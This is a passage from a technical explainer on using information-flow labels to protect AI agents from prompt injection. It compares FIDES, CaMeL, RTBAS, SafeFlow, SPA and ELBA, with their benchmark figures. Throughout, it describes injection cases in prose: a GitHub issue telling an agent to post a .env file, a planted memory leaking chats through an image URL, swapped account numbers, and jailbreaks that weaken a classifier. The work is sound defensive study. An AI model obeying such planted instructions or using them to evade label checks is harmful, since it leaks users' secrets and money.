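Two experimental features add the missing check. The setting `X-MCP-Features: ifc_labels` makes the GitHub MCP server label its results. The setting `FIDES_IFC=true` makes GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal, keep a context label and attach it to tool calls. If the user's request starts out trusted and public, the attack proceeds like this:

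| Step | Label on the new data | Context label afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| The user asks the agent to handle the issue | trusted, public | trusted, public |
| The agent reads the issue | untrusted, public | untrusted, public |
| The agent reads a file in contoso/core | trusted, private | untrusted, private |
| The agent proposes a public comment | untrusted, private | Policy check fails |

Copilot CLI then shows the user a dialog instead of posting the comment automatically. The full FIDES rule would also label the file untrusted, because an attacker influenced the request to read it, but this wouldn't change the context label.

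Microsoft's policy stops this comment because the context is both untrusted and private. An agent can comment without interruption if it reads only public repositories or works only within private ones. This avoids many unnecessary approval requests, but a malicious issue could still get the agent to post a misleading comment made entirely of public information.

The documentation for the server's label package, GitHub's *ifc* (2026), explains that files in public repositories are untrusted because anyone may have written them through a pull request (a proposed change to the code). Files in private repositories are trusted because only collaborators can change them. GitHub labels issues as untrusted even in private repositories, whereas Microsoft describes those issues as trusted. GitHub's choice is safer because a collaborator might paste a customer's email into a private issue, but it means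 that an agent would fail the trusted-context policy after reading almost any issue.

GitHub sends the word "private" instead of a list of readers, and the agent's side looks up the readers when the data is about to leave. When a search returns results from several repositories, the server labels the whole result private if any of those repositories is private. Two private repositories can have different collaborators, so whoever enforces the policy must still work out which repositories the results came from and allow only readers who have access to all of them.

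### The Microsoft Agent Framework module

Developers who build their own agents can use a FIDES module in Microsoft Agent Framework. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) introduced it on 20 May as an experimental feature in version 1.3.0 and later. Microsoft's documentation still describes it as experimental and Python-only.

Instead of reader sets, the module uses three confidentiality levels: public, private and user_identity, which covers personal data and credentials. It can't represent the Priya and Marco example exactly, because both emails would be labeled private. Developers can set `accepts_untrusted` to false to prevent a tool from running in an untrusted context, and use `max_allowed_confidentiality` to limit how sensitive the context may be when the tool runs.

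Microsoft demonstrates the module with an agent that sorts GitHub issues. One issue contains a hidden instruction to read a file named .env, where developers often keep passwords, and post its contents as a comment. Reading the issue makes the context untrusted. The agent may still read the file, but doing so makes the context private as well. The comment tool accepts only public contexts, so the module blocks the comment or asks the user, depending on the settings. If the instruction had been to overwrite a file, the module would have stopped the call because the writing tool doesn't accept an untrusted context.

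In its May post, Microsoft also says that the module refuses comments while any untrusted content remains in the context. But the settings in the example limit only the confidentiality of comments, so an attacker may still be able to influence a comment that contains only public data.

The labels in the example are also too broad. The agent reads files so that it can quote relevant source code, but its file-reading tool labels every file as private, so quoting any of them in a public comment triggers the policy. The tool would need to label public source files differently from the password file.

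If a developer forgets to label a tool's results, the module treats them as trusted and public according to Microsoft's May post, but as untrusted and public according to the undated documentation. Developers should set the default explicitly and test it. The untrusted default, which Microsoft describes as failing closed, does so only for integrity. If a tool returns unlabelled salary data, the module treats the data as public, and the permitted-readers check won't stop the agent from posting it.

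### Incomplete coverage and inferred labels

In June 2026, Copilot CLI enforced these policies only for selected tools on the GitHub MCP server and didn't support other MCP servers. Microsoft says the same method applies to shell commands, but someone still has to connect it to them. If a command reads a private file without updating the context label, later checks can miss a leak of that file's contents, just as a Dogwood rule fails when a read isn't recorded.

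Microsoft has released an open-source gateway that adds labels and policies to existing servers. It supports selected tools from Work IQ, Microsoft's servers for services such as mail and Teams. Adding another server requires, for each tool, a description of the structure of its output, a Python function that calculates the labels, and a policy.

A quicker approach is to infer labels and policies from tool annotations, the hints about a tool's behaviour that MCP servers can provide. A closed-world tool works only within a limited set of data, while an open-world tool, such as web search, can interact with outside sources. Microsoft suggests these rules:

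| Annotation | Inferred policy |
|---|---|
| Read-only and closed-world | Always allow |
| Read-only and open-world | Allow only if every argument is public |
| Destructive | Ask the user |

Results from open-world tools would be untrusted, and results from tools that require a login would be private. Each result would also inherit the labels of the tool call's arguments.

The inferred labels, which Microsoft calls safe, depend on accurate annotations. A developer might reasonably annotate a mailbox search as closed-world because it searches only one mailbox, even though strangers wrote many of the emails in it. The results would then lack the untrusted label they need. The annotations also don't specify who may read the data, so a policy based on them couldn't distinguish Priya from Marco.

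MCP had no agreed format for these labels in June 2026, and Microsoft planned to develop a proposal with the protocol's community. GitHub's label package was in version 1.0.5 of its server, published on 18 May, and in version 1.1.1, which GitHub (2026) published on 29 May. According to the Go package index, the latest version of the server's module doesn't contain the package or the directory around it, so GitHub may have reorganised the code without removing the feature. A company using the labels should check after each update that results from a private repository still have one.

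## How labels on model output differ from labels on files

GitHub's server labels a file in contoso/core as private because the repository is private, a fact that software can look up. If an agent reads that file and then drafts a comment, Copilot CLI treats the comment as private too, even if it only thanks sofiagarcia for her report. Nobody can yet trace exactly which inputs shaped the comment's wording, so the label is based on the cautious assumption that anything in the context may have.

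### What the label belongs to

| | Label on a file | Label on model output |
|---|---|---|
| Who assigns it | The operating system, following an administrator's rules | The harness, by joining the labels in the context |
| What it belongs to | One file, which the system can always identify | A piece of text, such as a reply or an argument of a tool call |
| How it follows the content | Usually stays the same when a permitted program edits the file | Covers everything the model read, including text it didn't use |
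| What happens on copying | The system labels the new file by rule | The label survives only if software copies it along with the text |
| What happens on storage and reuse | The label stays on the disk, and the system checks it whenever a program opens the file | The label survives only if the store has a place for it and the next harness reads it |

File labels can be inexact. Under Bell and LaPadula's rules, a file written by a process working at top secret is labeled top secret, whatever it contains. SELinux normally gives a new file the type of the directory it is in, so a copy may have a different label from the original. Copying the file to a memory stick whose format can't store labels loses the label.

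With an ordinary program, engineers can track labels more precisely by doing more work. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) notes that classical systems track labels on processor instructions, program variables, processes or whole file systems. An engineer who needs to know whether a salary reaches a log file can follow the variable through the source code, but can't trace it through a model's weights in the same way. The paper concludes that, for now, a harness can only assume that the output has the labels of all the model's inputs, which leads to label creep.

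Labelling inputs more finely, for example by labelling each passage of a web page with the site it came from, doesn't by itself make the output's label more precise. If one of ten emails is secret, joining their ten labels gives the output a secret label, just as a single secret label on the whole list would. The separate labels help only if the harness can keep the secret email from the model or establish that it had no influence on the output.

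### A harmless summary with a secret label

Suppose an agent has read a confidential plan to close the Leeds office, along with the public menu of the Leeds canteen. The user asks for a summary of the menu. The summary contains nothing about the closure, but the harness labels it confidential.

If the summary adds that the canteen needn't order supplies for spring, it reveals the plan without repeating a word of it. A person comparing the two texts might miss this and call the summary's label wrong. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) defines influence broadly enough to cover this case. An input reaches the output if the output visibly copies or transforms it, or if the input determines a decision, a selection, a computed value or the format. By this definition, a one-word answer such as "reject" needs the label of the confidential assessment it was based on.

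Xu and colleagues also studied open-source programs that fill slots in a prompt with data and send the prompt to a model. In code from 2,103 families of repositories, the data in 12 to 14% of the filled slots didn't influence the output, so joining the labels of all the inputs was right for about seven slots in eight. A broad label therefore isn't necessarily wrong, although an agent that has made fifty tool calls probably has more unused text in its context.

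### Labels lost in storage

An agent might paraphrase a confidential email and save the paraphrase with a note-taking tool that stores only text. The paraphrase then loses its confidentiality label, so a later session reads the note as ordinary data.

*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) illustrates the same problem with two messaging tools. One is allowed to send private text, and the other returns sent messages with a public label. If an agent sends its user a private message and then reads it back, the text comes back labeled public, even though each tool followed its own policy.

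The default label determines what the agent can do with the unlabelled note. Zhong and colleagues treat text without a label as public and trusted, so the agent could send the paraphrase anywhere. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, suggest giving such text the most restrictive label. That protects the paraphrase but may prevent the agent from using its own harmless notes.

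Storage can also make untrusted text look trusted. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses an attack on ChatGPT's macOS app, in which a malicious document or website planted instructions in the Memories feature, which was presumably meant to hold the user's own preferences. The instructions made the app send the user's later conversations to the attacker's server in the address of an invisible image.

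A bad note in an agent's memory can be harder to notice than a misplaced file. Kim, Liu and colleagues (2026) explain in *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* that agents often store memories as vectors, lists of numbers that represent meaning, and retrieve them by similarity. The note may therefore come up much later in a conversation about something else.

One remedy is to store the label in a field beside the text, but this works only if every tool fills in the field and every harness reads it. A simpler remedy is to keep separate stores, such as one folder for notes from confidential sessions and another for the rest. The operating system's label on the folder then protects the notes even when the text has lost its own label. However, trivial notes in the confidential folder are also treated as confidential.

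### Invented and remembered facts

Model output can be labeled trusted and still be false. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a plumber. The context contains only the user's request and the company's supplier list, which has no account number for the plumber, so the model makes one up. Because every input was trusted, the number is labeled trusted too, and the trusted-context policy allows the payment.

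The label correctly shows that no outsider influenced the number. A file label also wouldn't reveal that a clerk had mistyped an account number. But the clerk was probably copying from an invoice, which an auditor can check, while there is no original to check the model's number against. A rule like the one AWS wrote for transfers, which requires a recent lookup to have returned the same number, would stop the payment.

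A fact the model recalls from training usually has a source, but the harness can't identify it. If an agent fetches a web page to find a bank's telephone number, the harness labels the number untrusted. If the model recalls the number from the same page in its training data, the number counts as trusted, because Costa and colleagues include the choice of model in the trusted configuration. Similarly, if a company trains a model on its personnel files, the model could repeat them in an answer labeled public.

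A harness could give the model its own label *M* and label each output

*C* ⊔ *M*,

where *C* is the context label. For the model trained on personnel files, *M* should be private, which makes every answer private. Integrity is harder to handle. Many models learn from web pages that strangers wrote, so a strict administrator would set *M* to untrusted. Every output would then be untrusted, and the trusted-context policy would block every consequential action.

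Treating the model as trusted is a practical compromise, but labels then can't detect poisoned training data. Kim and colleagues rate attacks on the agent's internals, including backdoors planted in the model, as the most severe kind but less practical than other attacks.

### Code that the model writes

An agent that reads a stranger's bug report may write a script to fix the problem. The harness labels the script's text untrusted and can refuse to run it. If the script runs, the operating system sets the new process's permissions from the user account, the sandbox and, under type enforcement, the types of the parent process and the program file. It does not use the labels in the agent's messages, so a script labelled public can still open a confidential file if its account can, and a trusted label gives no extra access.

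The script's output then needs a label too, and under Costa and colleagues' rule that label must cover everything the script could have read. If the script can read most of the disk, even the message "tests passed" gets the same confidentiality label as the most sensitive file it can read. A narrower sandbox allows a less restrictive label, because the harness can exclude files the script couldn't open.

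The harness can enforce a script's own label by choosing a sandbox to match it, for example by running untrusted scripts without network access or credentials. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* compares this with web browsers, which can limit where a page's scripts come from and what embedded content may do. Most scripts on a web page come from an address that the browser can check. But an agent's script may combine ideas from a bug report, a manual and the user's request, so the harness has to choose the sandbox according to the least trusted of these sources.

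### Keeping restricted text from the model

A harness can justify a less restrictive label by generating the output without the restricted text. Siddiqui and colleagues' system first produces an answer *y* from all the documents. It then tests whether the model would have been nearly as likely to give *y* if it had seen only the documents labelled L′ or lower. With *U* as a score for how well the model predicts *y*, the label L′ is acceptable if

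*U*(all documents) − *U*(documents at or below L′) ≤ λ,

where the developer chooses the tolerance λ. The system then discards *y*, runs the model again on the smaller set of documents and returns the new answer with the label L′.

In one example, a user asks how many people live in New York City. A trusted source gives about 8.4 million and an untrusted source about 8 million. Since the trusted source is sufficient, the system regenerates the answer from that source alone, and the answer is trusted.

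The second run protects the label from a malicious document. Such a document may mislead the search for L′, but if the system leaves it out, the model never reads it when writing the final answer. A mistake in the search can make the answer worse without making its label too permissive. The excluded documents may still have had a small influence on which label the system chose, because they influenced the first answer.

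Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method mainly on Llama 2 models. In a synthetic test with 14 documents per question, the method found exactly the right labels for 86% of questions. Asking the model which documents it had used gave correct results for only 2% of questions with the smaller model and 13% with the larger. In a test with news articles, a better label was possible for 647 questions, and the method found it for 57% of them with the smaller model and 39% with the larger.

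In the news test, the system wrongly dropped a label in about 19 to 23% of the cases where it relaxed the label. In those cases, the second run would lack a document the answer needed. In a small set of agent conversations, the system improved on the baseline's label in more than 85% of cases, though this percentage presumably refers only to the 20 of 40 conversations where improvement was possible.

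Zhong and colleagues avoid the first draft by choosing the relevant text in advance. Their system, RTBAS, works in four steps:

1. A screener picks out the parts of the history that the next response needs.
2. The harness joins the labels of those parts.
3. It hides every part of the history with a label that may not flow to the joined label.
4. The model writes its response from what remains, and the harness checks any tool call against the joined label.

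The screener can be a second language model that reads the whole history and names the relevant parts, or a small neural network that uses attention scores, which estimate how much each piece of input affected an output. Zhong and colleagues take these scores from a small open model, so the method also works with commercial models whose internals they can't inspect. They trained the network on 40 test cases, and it classified 81% of the test data correctly.

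That accuracy is less worrying because the label stays correct even when the screener is wrong. In the paper's example, a stranger hides an instruction in a payment's description, telling the agent to send $100. If the screener considers the description irrelevant, the harness hides it and the model can't follow the instruction. If the screener considers it relevant, the context becomes untrusted and the agent needs the user's confirmation before sending money. An attacker who fools the screener can therefore cause unnecessary confirmation requests or a poor answer, but can't get the model to read the instruction under a trusted label.

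This protection depends on correct initial labels. If the payment tool doesn't label the description, RTBAS treats it as public and trusted, so it never hides it. Zhong and colleagues report that, with integrity labels in place, RTBAS stopped every targeted attack in the AgentDojo benchmark and reduced task completion under attack by only 2%.

### Estimating influence from attention

Sightline, Xu and colleagues' tool, analyses a finished call and removes the labels of inputs it classifies as unused. It does this without hiding anything or running the model again to produce a new answer. In a standard transformer, only attention moves information from one token's position to another. Xu and colleagues prove that an input has no influence on the output if no later position attends to it, at least for small changes to the input.

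In practice, a model attends to every input at least slightly, and the amount of attention is a poor guide to influence. A model can attend strongly to a passage without using it. Weak attention doesn't rule out influence either. Xu and colleagues construct a case in which the attention on an input is about 2 × 10⁻⁹, yet changing that input reverses the answer. In their real data, no input that influenced an output received so little attention.

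Sightline therefore learns from labelled examples which patterns of attention indicate use, then sets a threshold to limit its errors. Suppose a developer accepts a miss rate of α = 1% and has examples from *n* = 999 families of repositories. Sightline scores one randomly chosen true influence from each family and sets the threshold at the *k*th lowest score, where

*k* = ⌊α(*n* + 1)⌋ = 10.

If a new family resembles the old ones, a true influence drawn from it in the same way has at most a 1% chance of scoring below the threshold.

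Xu and colleagues report that, in the tests, Sightline missed about 1% of true influences and removed 44 to 66% of the unnecessary labels. It also removed about half of the unnecessary labels in an agent, and no attack call got past a policy against untrusted actions.

The 1% limit is an average over calls like those in the examples, and an attacker can write text unlike any of them. If Sightline wrongly removes an untrusted label, output that the attacker's text has influenced looks trusted. Hiding text or answering again avoids this risk but changes the answer. Sightline seems better suited to reducing false alarms in an audit than to deciding by itself whether a payment may go ahead.

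### Labels inferred from content

A label based on a file's source can miss a password in an ordinary document. *SafeFlow* (Dai, Ying and colleagues, 2026) uses a language model to look for such risks in the content of a request. The model chooses from seven labels, including ones for credential access, sending data outside and attempts to override instructions. Fixed rules carry these labels across agents and steps, and hold back irreversible actions until the system has checked the whole chain.

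For example, one agent might read a configuration file, a second might extract a login token from it, and a third might email the token to an outsider. Each step may look acceptable on its own. SafeFlow keeps the credential label on the work as it passes between the agents, so it can block the email.

A model assigns the labels by reading text, so an attacker who controls the wording of that text may be able to influence them. Dai and colleagues tested SafeFlow on harmful tasks, both stated plainly and reworded with four jailbreak techniques meant to get past a model's safeguards. The last column below shows the attack success rate with SafeFlow divided by the rate with no defense.

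| Form of the request | Undefended system | SafeFlow | Ratio |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain | 69.3% | 12.7% | 18% |
| MultiLingual | 74.1% | 19.1% | 26% |
| GPTFuzz | 76.4% | 20.9% | 27% |
| ReNeLLM | 80.5% | 25.5% | 32% |
| JailBroken | 85.5% | 32.3% | 38% |

The jailbreaks made the undefended system more vulnerable too, but the rising ratio suggests that they also weakened SafeFlow. The figures don't separate wrong labels from errors in later stages that also use a model. The jailbreaks were general-purpose, so an attacker who studied SafeFlow's classifier might succeed more often.

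SafeFlow completed 89 to 92% of harmless tasks, compared with 94 to 97% for the undefended system. A company could use content labels more safely by joining them with labels based on the source:

ℓ_source ⊔ ℓ_content.

The classifier could then add restrictions but never remove any, like a model judge that can only veto. This would also partly protect notes that had lost their original labels.

### Graded labels

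Ordinary labels don't distinguish between an output that a source slightly influenced and one that copies the source completely. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests graded labels that estimate how much information an output contains about each source. It also proposes measuring influence by removing or altering inputs, or by tracing the computation inside the model. These are research directions, and the paper reports no measurements for them.

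A policy engine would still have to turn the grade into a decision. Suppose it allows any output that reveals at most one bit about a four-digit PIN. The PIN contains log₂ 10,000 ≈ 13.3 bits, so 14 well-chosen yes-or-no answers could reveal all of it. The engine would therefore need to add up leaks across answers and sessions. Small influences can also seriously damage integrity, as when a hidden instruction changes one digit of an account number.

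The grades themselves may be wrong. Xu and colleagues show that if two documents contain the same fact, removing either one may change nothing, so a test that removes one document at a time could find that neither had any influence. On inputs with duplicated content, such a test ranked a used input above an unused one only 54 to 69% of the time, where 50% is chance. An attacker who can put the same text in two places could exploit this. (Duplicates don't endanger Siddiqui and colleagues' labels, because their system generates the final answer from whichever documents remain.)

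Measuring the effect of tiny changes to an input can understate that input's influence when the model is almost certain of its answer. A tiny change then barely affects the probabilities, even if a larger change to the same input would reverse the answer. The document that decided a near-certain approval or rejection could therefore get a low grade.

### Who makes a label binding

A model that helps assign labels also helps decide what agents may do. Lee and Lee let agents draft policies but not put them into force, because agents subject to a policy may also be its authors, a problem they call the authorship hazard. They define the author as the party whose act makes a policy binding, whoever wrote the text.

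The agent that drafts the policy and the agent that must obey it can be separate programs. In Lee and Lee's system, the drafting agent works for the company that supplies the data, and the agent that must obey the policy works for the company that receives it. Lee and Lee nevertheless treat the two agents as one party, partly because the receiving company could influence the drafting agent. For instance, it could plant an instruction in a column name to shape the policy that will restrict its own agents.

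Whoever classifies data also helps decide what a policy permits. In one of Lee and Lee's examples, a policy requires the system to anonymise three fields that identify companies, including the consignee, who receives the goods. An agent proposes moving the consignee field to the class for public trade facts. To a reviewer, this may look like a routine correction, since the policy's text stays the same and the system still anonymises the other two fields. In the tests, moving one identity field this way permitted 80 requests that the system had previously denied.

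Bell and LaPadula's model avoids this problem by assuming that nobody changes a label while it is in use. Lee and Lee instead propose human review, which takes time. In a set of 380 constructed drafts, requiring review of changes to classifications, the shared vocabulary and the checking software raised the share of drafts needing extra review from 37% to 71%. The set contained many attacks, and Lee and Lee estimate that about 3% of drafts would need extra review if 99% were harmless and few of those changed a classification.

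People can't approve every label a harness assigns while an agent is running, but Lee and Lee's definition is still useful because it directs attention to what makes each label binding. In Siddiqui and colleagues' system and in RTBAS, a model may help choose the label, but fixed code then withholds any text the label doesn't cover. SafeFlow applies its classifier's labels without a similar safeguard, and agents that rely on Sightline accept its decisions to remove labels. Anyone who can fool those classifiers gains some control over what the agent may do.

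## Label creep and ways to limit it

An agent's context label can only become more restrictive as the agent reads. Over a long task, restrictions build up until the policy engine blocks harmless actions along with dangerous ones, a problem called label creep. Removing labels afterwards, as Sightline does, risks removing one that should have stayed. Several newer designs instead keep restricted text away from the planner, so its label doesn't spread to every later choice.

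### A six-call task

Suppose a user asks an agent to list Friday's appointments, forward the supplier's latest email to Priya, save a copy in the meeting notes and book Room 4 for 3 p.m. The calendar and address book are trusted, but the email is not. The last two columns give the integrity label on the agent's choice of each call.

| Call | Depends on | Email text in the context | Email text in a variable |
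|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Read Friday's calendar | The request | Trusted | Trusted |
| 2. Look up Priya's address | The request | Trusted | Trusted |
| 3. Read the supplier's email | The request | Trusted | Trusted |
| 4. Forward the email to Priya | The request, the address and the email | Untrusted | Trusted |
| 5. Save a copy in the notes | The request and the email | Untrusted | Trusted |
| 6. Book Room 4 for 3 p.m. | The request | Untrusted | Trusted |

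In the third column, call 3 makes the context label untrusted, and calls 4 to 6 inherit that label. The room booking depends only on the user's request, but the trusted-context policy blocks it along with the others.

In the last column, the harness stores the email in its own memory and gives the planner only a name for it, such as #read_email_0. The planner can pass the name as an argument, and the harness replaces it with the email's text when it makes the call. Since the planner never reads the email, a hidden instruction in it can't influence the choice of calls 4 to 6.

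The text is still untrusted. The strict trusted-context policy requires every argument to be trusted, so it would now allow the room booking but still block calls 4 and 5. Costa and colleagues therefore propose more detailed policies, which might require a trusted choice of tool and a trusted recipient but accept an untrusted message body. All six calls succeed under such a policy. Priya may receive a misleading email, but the user asked the agent to forward it.

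### The dual-model pattern

A model can forward an email without understanding it, but it can't summarise one that way. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed dividing the work between two models. A privileged model has the tools but never reads untrusted text, which goes instead to a quarantined model with no tools. The two communicate only through variables, which the software around them manages.

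Costa and colleagues show how such an agent could summarise three emails and send the result to a colleague:

1. The planner calls the mail tool, and the harness stores the emails in a variable.
2. The planner asks the quarantined model to summarise that variable, and the harness stores the summary in a second variable.
3. The planner calls the messaging tool with the colleague's name and the second variable.

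An instruction in one of the emails can still change what the quarantined model writes, for example by making it produce an empty summary. It can't make the model send anything, because the model has no tools. A policy that allows only trusted messages to be sent would block the empty summary, but it would also block every accurate summary of an outside email.

Separating the planner from the quarantined model does not make extracted values safe. If the user asks the agent to pay an invoice, the quarantined model may extract an attacker's account number from it. The planner then calls the correct payment tool but sends the money to the attacker. Labels on tool arguments therefore still matter when the planner is well protected.

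### Data-independent and data-dependent tasks

The pattern works only if the planner can choose its calls without reading the hidden text. Costa and colleagues define this condition exactly. A task consists of a user's request, a list of tools and a set *D* of possible starting datastores, such as all the mailboxes the user might have. For each datastore *d*, let *S*(*d*) be the set of action sequences that complete the task, ignoring queries to the model. The task is data-independent if

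⋂ *S*(*d*) ≠ ∅, taken over all *d* in *D*.

In other words, at least one fixed sequence works whatever the mailbox contains. Forwarding the latest email meets this condition, because the sequence can refer to the email by name. Summarising the email also meets the condition if the agent can call a quarantined model.

The task "Create a calendar event if one of my emails asks for a meeting" is data-dependent because the emails determine whether an event is needed, so no single sequence of tool calls works for every mailbox. "Complete today's tasks in my to-do app" is even harder, since the tasks could require almost any tool.

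The percentages Costa and colleagues report for AgentDojo imply that 77 of its 97 user tasks are data-independent. Of these, 26 need only variables and 51 also need a quarantined model. The other 20 are data-dependent, 16 of them in the banking and Slack suites. An agent that can't handle data-dependent tasks may therefore do well as an office assistant but poorly in banking.

### Hiding only what would raise the label

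The simplest variable-passing agent hides every tool result, including trusted ones that would help the planner. Costa and colleagues' FIDES hides a result, or a field of a structured result, only if its label would make the context label more restrictive. In a list of emails, the planner might read trusted timestamps while the harness replaces the subjects and bodies with variable names.

The planner can also open a variable with a tool called inspect. FIDES then adds the variable's label to the context label and restricts later calls as it would in an ordinary agent. For a data-dependent task, the planner can first have the quarantined model reduce the text to a yes-or-no answer. If the policy allows such answers despite their untrusted source, the agent can act on them.

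Costa and colleagues tested FIDES in 2025 using AgentDojo attacks in which the attacker knows which tools the agent has. Without policy checks, a basic planner running on GPT-4o carried out 152 injected actions, and FIDES carried out 21. FIDES still carried out some because nothing prevented its planner from opening an untrusted variable and acting on it. With policy checks, neither planner carried out any injected actions.

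These zeros are weaker evidence than they seem, because Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it. The labels therefore covered every place where an attack could appear. After reviewing the attacks that AgentDojo counted as successful, they also excluded some, including those that changed only the wording of a text. The results are good evidence that the checks work when the labels are right, but they don't show whether an administrator would label the right fields.

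The more informative comparison is how much ordinary work each planner completed when there was no attack. These are the results with GPT-4o.

| Suite | Data-dependent tasks | Basic planner, no checks | Basic planner, with checks | FIDES, with checks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 5.0% | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 10.0% | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 43.8% | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
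| Slack | 42.9% | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic planner under the same checks, averaged over the four suites. With OpenAI's o1 model, the advantage was 16 points. But with GPT-4o, FIDES completed about 50% of tasks, compared with 84% for the unprotected planner, so it recovered only a small part of the tasks lost to the checks.

Travel is the exception, because many of its tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context as long as no confidential data leaves. The checks therefore didn't lower the basic planner's completion rate, but FIDES did worse because GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks with o1, compared with 41% with GPT-4o.

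The variables themselves make the planner's work harder. With the policy checks off, FIDES's task completion rate on GPT-4o was 23.7 percentage points lower than the basic planner's. In their introduction, Costa and colleagues give the drop as only 6.3%, which may refer to o1. Some tasks failed because the planner confused variable names or made unnecessary calls. In one Slack task, the planner fetched a list of channels even though the user had already named the channel, and the list made the context untrusted.

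Hiding text can also lead to poorly informed decisions. In one banking task, the agent was asked to change the user's password if it found a suspicious transaction. The planner could read the transactions' amounts and dates, but their subject lines were in variables. It judged a large payment suspicious and changed the password without reading the subject line. This counted as a success in AgentDojo and broke no policy. If the subject line had shown a harmless purpose, such as a house deposit, the change might have been unnecessary.

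### Writing the whole program in advance

FIDES chooses one action at a time. CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, has the privileged model turn the user's request into a program before the agent reads any data. Willison credits CaMeL with fixing a flaw in his dual-model pattern. He gives the example "Send Bob the document he requested in our last meeting". For this request, the program might search the meeting notes, have a quarantined model extract the document's name, fetch the file and send it to Bob.

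An interpreter runs the program and checks the inputs and outputs of each step. Each value carries a record of where it came from and who may receive it. If a false note names a confidential file, the program may fetch that file, but the interpreter can keep the file from reaching Bob if he isn't permitted to read it. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, point out that CaMeL's policies can express more than label comparisons, but that its guarantees depend on someone writing a correct policy for each tool.

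Since CaMeL's privileged model writes the program without reading the data, it can't write steps that only the data would suggest. For the to-do list, it could write a loop over the tasks, but it would have to guess in advance which tools the tasks would need.

Girrens and Wang's own system, SPA, also plans in advance and extends the protection to later requests. It calls the planner once per request, and the planner writes a complete plan using six kinds of step:

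- retrieve a stored result;
- call a tool;
- query a quarantined model;
- display something to the user;
- choose between two branches;
- repeat steps for each item in a list.

Before any tool runs, SPA calculates the labels for the whole plan, including both branches of every condition. If a tool call would break a policy, SPA rejects the plan and doesn't request another. This prevents half-finished tasks, but one forbidden step also blocks all the permitted ones. In the six-call task, if the messaging tool requires trusted inputs, the agent doesn't book the room.

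In Girrens and Wang's example of a delayed attack, a user asks the agent on Monday to fetch an invoice from Acme and remember its details. An attacker has changed the account number in the invoice. On Tuesday the user says, "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". SPA has stored the details with their untrusted label and shows Tuesday's planner only a description of them. The planner writes a plan to retrieve the details and pay. If the payment tool requires trusted inputs, SPA rejects the plan.

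For the same reason, SPA would reject a plan to pay a genuine invoice. Taking the account number from a trusted supplier list wouldn't be enough if the amount still came from the invoice, because SPA applies one integrity requirement to all of a tool's arguments. Girrens and Wang suggest a separate requirement for each argument as future work.

The tests ran SPA with gpt-5.4-nano on AgentDojo and on a version of AgentDojo that splits each task into two to five requests. The middle column shows the results for SPA's advance planning without label checks.

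| Measure | Planning in advance | With label checks |
|---|---|---|
| Successful attacks, single request | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Tasks completed, single request | 53.0% | 29.0% |
| Successful attacks, several requests | 0.3% | 0.2% |
| Tasks completed, several requests | 62.5% | 35.3% |

Advance planning kept successful attacks to 4 in 949 in the single-request test. Label checks stopped those four but cut the share of completed tasks by 24 percentage points. SPA rejected the plan because of its labels in about 53% of trials, typically when untrusted tool output would become an argument to a tool that required trusted data.

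That looks like a poor trade-off, but most of the attacks planted instructions, which planning in advance already resists. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that they hardly tested attacks placed in stored data to take effect during a later request. Label checks would probably have helped more against attacks that replaced account numbers.

With label checks on, later plans retrieved the labelled results they needed from earlier requests 89.9% of the time. An optional mode also hides the installed tools' descriptions from the planner, so SPA has to match the hypothetical tools in the plan to real ones. About three-quarters of trials in this mode failed at that step.

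### Letting quarantined agents use tools

A quarantined model without tools can't follow a link in an email or look up a word it doesn't recognise. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, argue that labels make a complete ban on tools unnecessary. In their system, ELBA, the agent writes short programs in Haskell, where a program's type specifies what kinds of effect it may have. ELBA checks the type before running a program and returns any error to the model so it can try again.

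One of their examples is ELBA, an agent that writes bibliographies using only records from DBLP, a computer-science database. The function that writes to the bibliography accepts only values of a "trusted record" type, which the agent can get only by fetching them from DBLP. A program that makes up a record or writes to the file by another route fails the type check. In 100 tasks with Claude Sonnet 5, none of ELBA's 925 citations had a false author, year or DOI, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with web search.

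ELBA uses an existing Haskell library, LIO, to track information-flow labels while the program runs, so a program can pass the type check and still stop partway through because of a label. SPA avoids this by checking the whole plan before running it, but it can't change the plan in response to what the tools return.

An ELBA agent can start a sub-agent in an isolated block. The sub-agent can read a stranger's message, which makes its label more restrictive, and still call any tool the new label permits. It returns a sealed result, which the main agent can pass to a tool without opening, so the main agent's label stays the same. The dual-model pattern is a special case of this design in which the sub-agent has no tools.

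Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks, using newer models than Costa and colleagues used. The table shows how many tasks each system completed when it was not under attack.

| Model | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies on | ELBA, policies off | CaMeL, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT 5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
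| Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

ELBA's advantage when policies are enforced suggests that letting sub-agents use tools helps. But the comparison covers only 21 tasks, and the 95% confidence interval for the difference includes zero for Opus 4.8. Zhou and colleagues also wrote new policies for ELBA, which lower an agent's privileges to those of any source it reads, so some of the gap may come from the policies rather than the design. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL.

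Both systems resisted all of AgentDojo's standard attacks, even with their policies turned off. The models themselves had become good at ignoring these attacks, so the benchmark no longer showed whether the policies helped. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a worse case. Whenever a sub-agent received an injected instruction, they removed its real task and gave it only the attacker's text.

Turning policies on reduced the success rate of these forced attacks from 16–42%, depending on the model, to zero across 735 attacks on each model. It also reduced task completion from 67–76% to 40–48%. Forced attacks are a better test of enforcement outside the model because the result doesn't depend on the model recognising the attack.

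### Recovering from a blocked call

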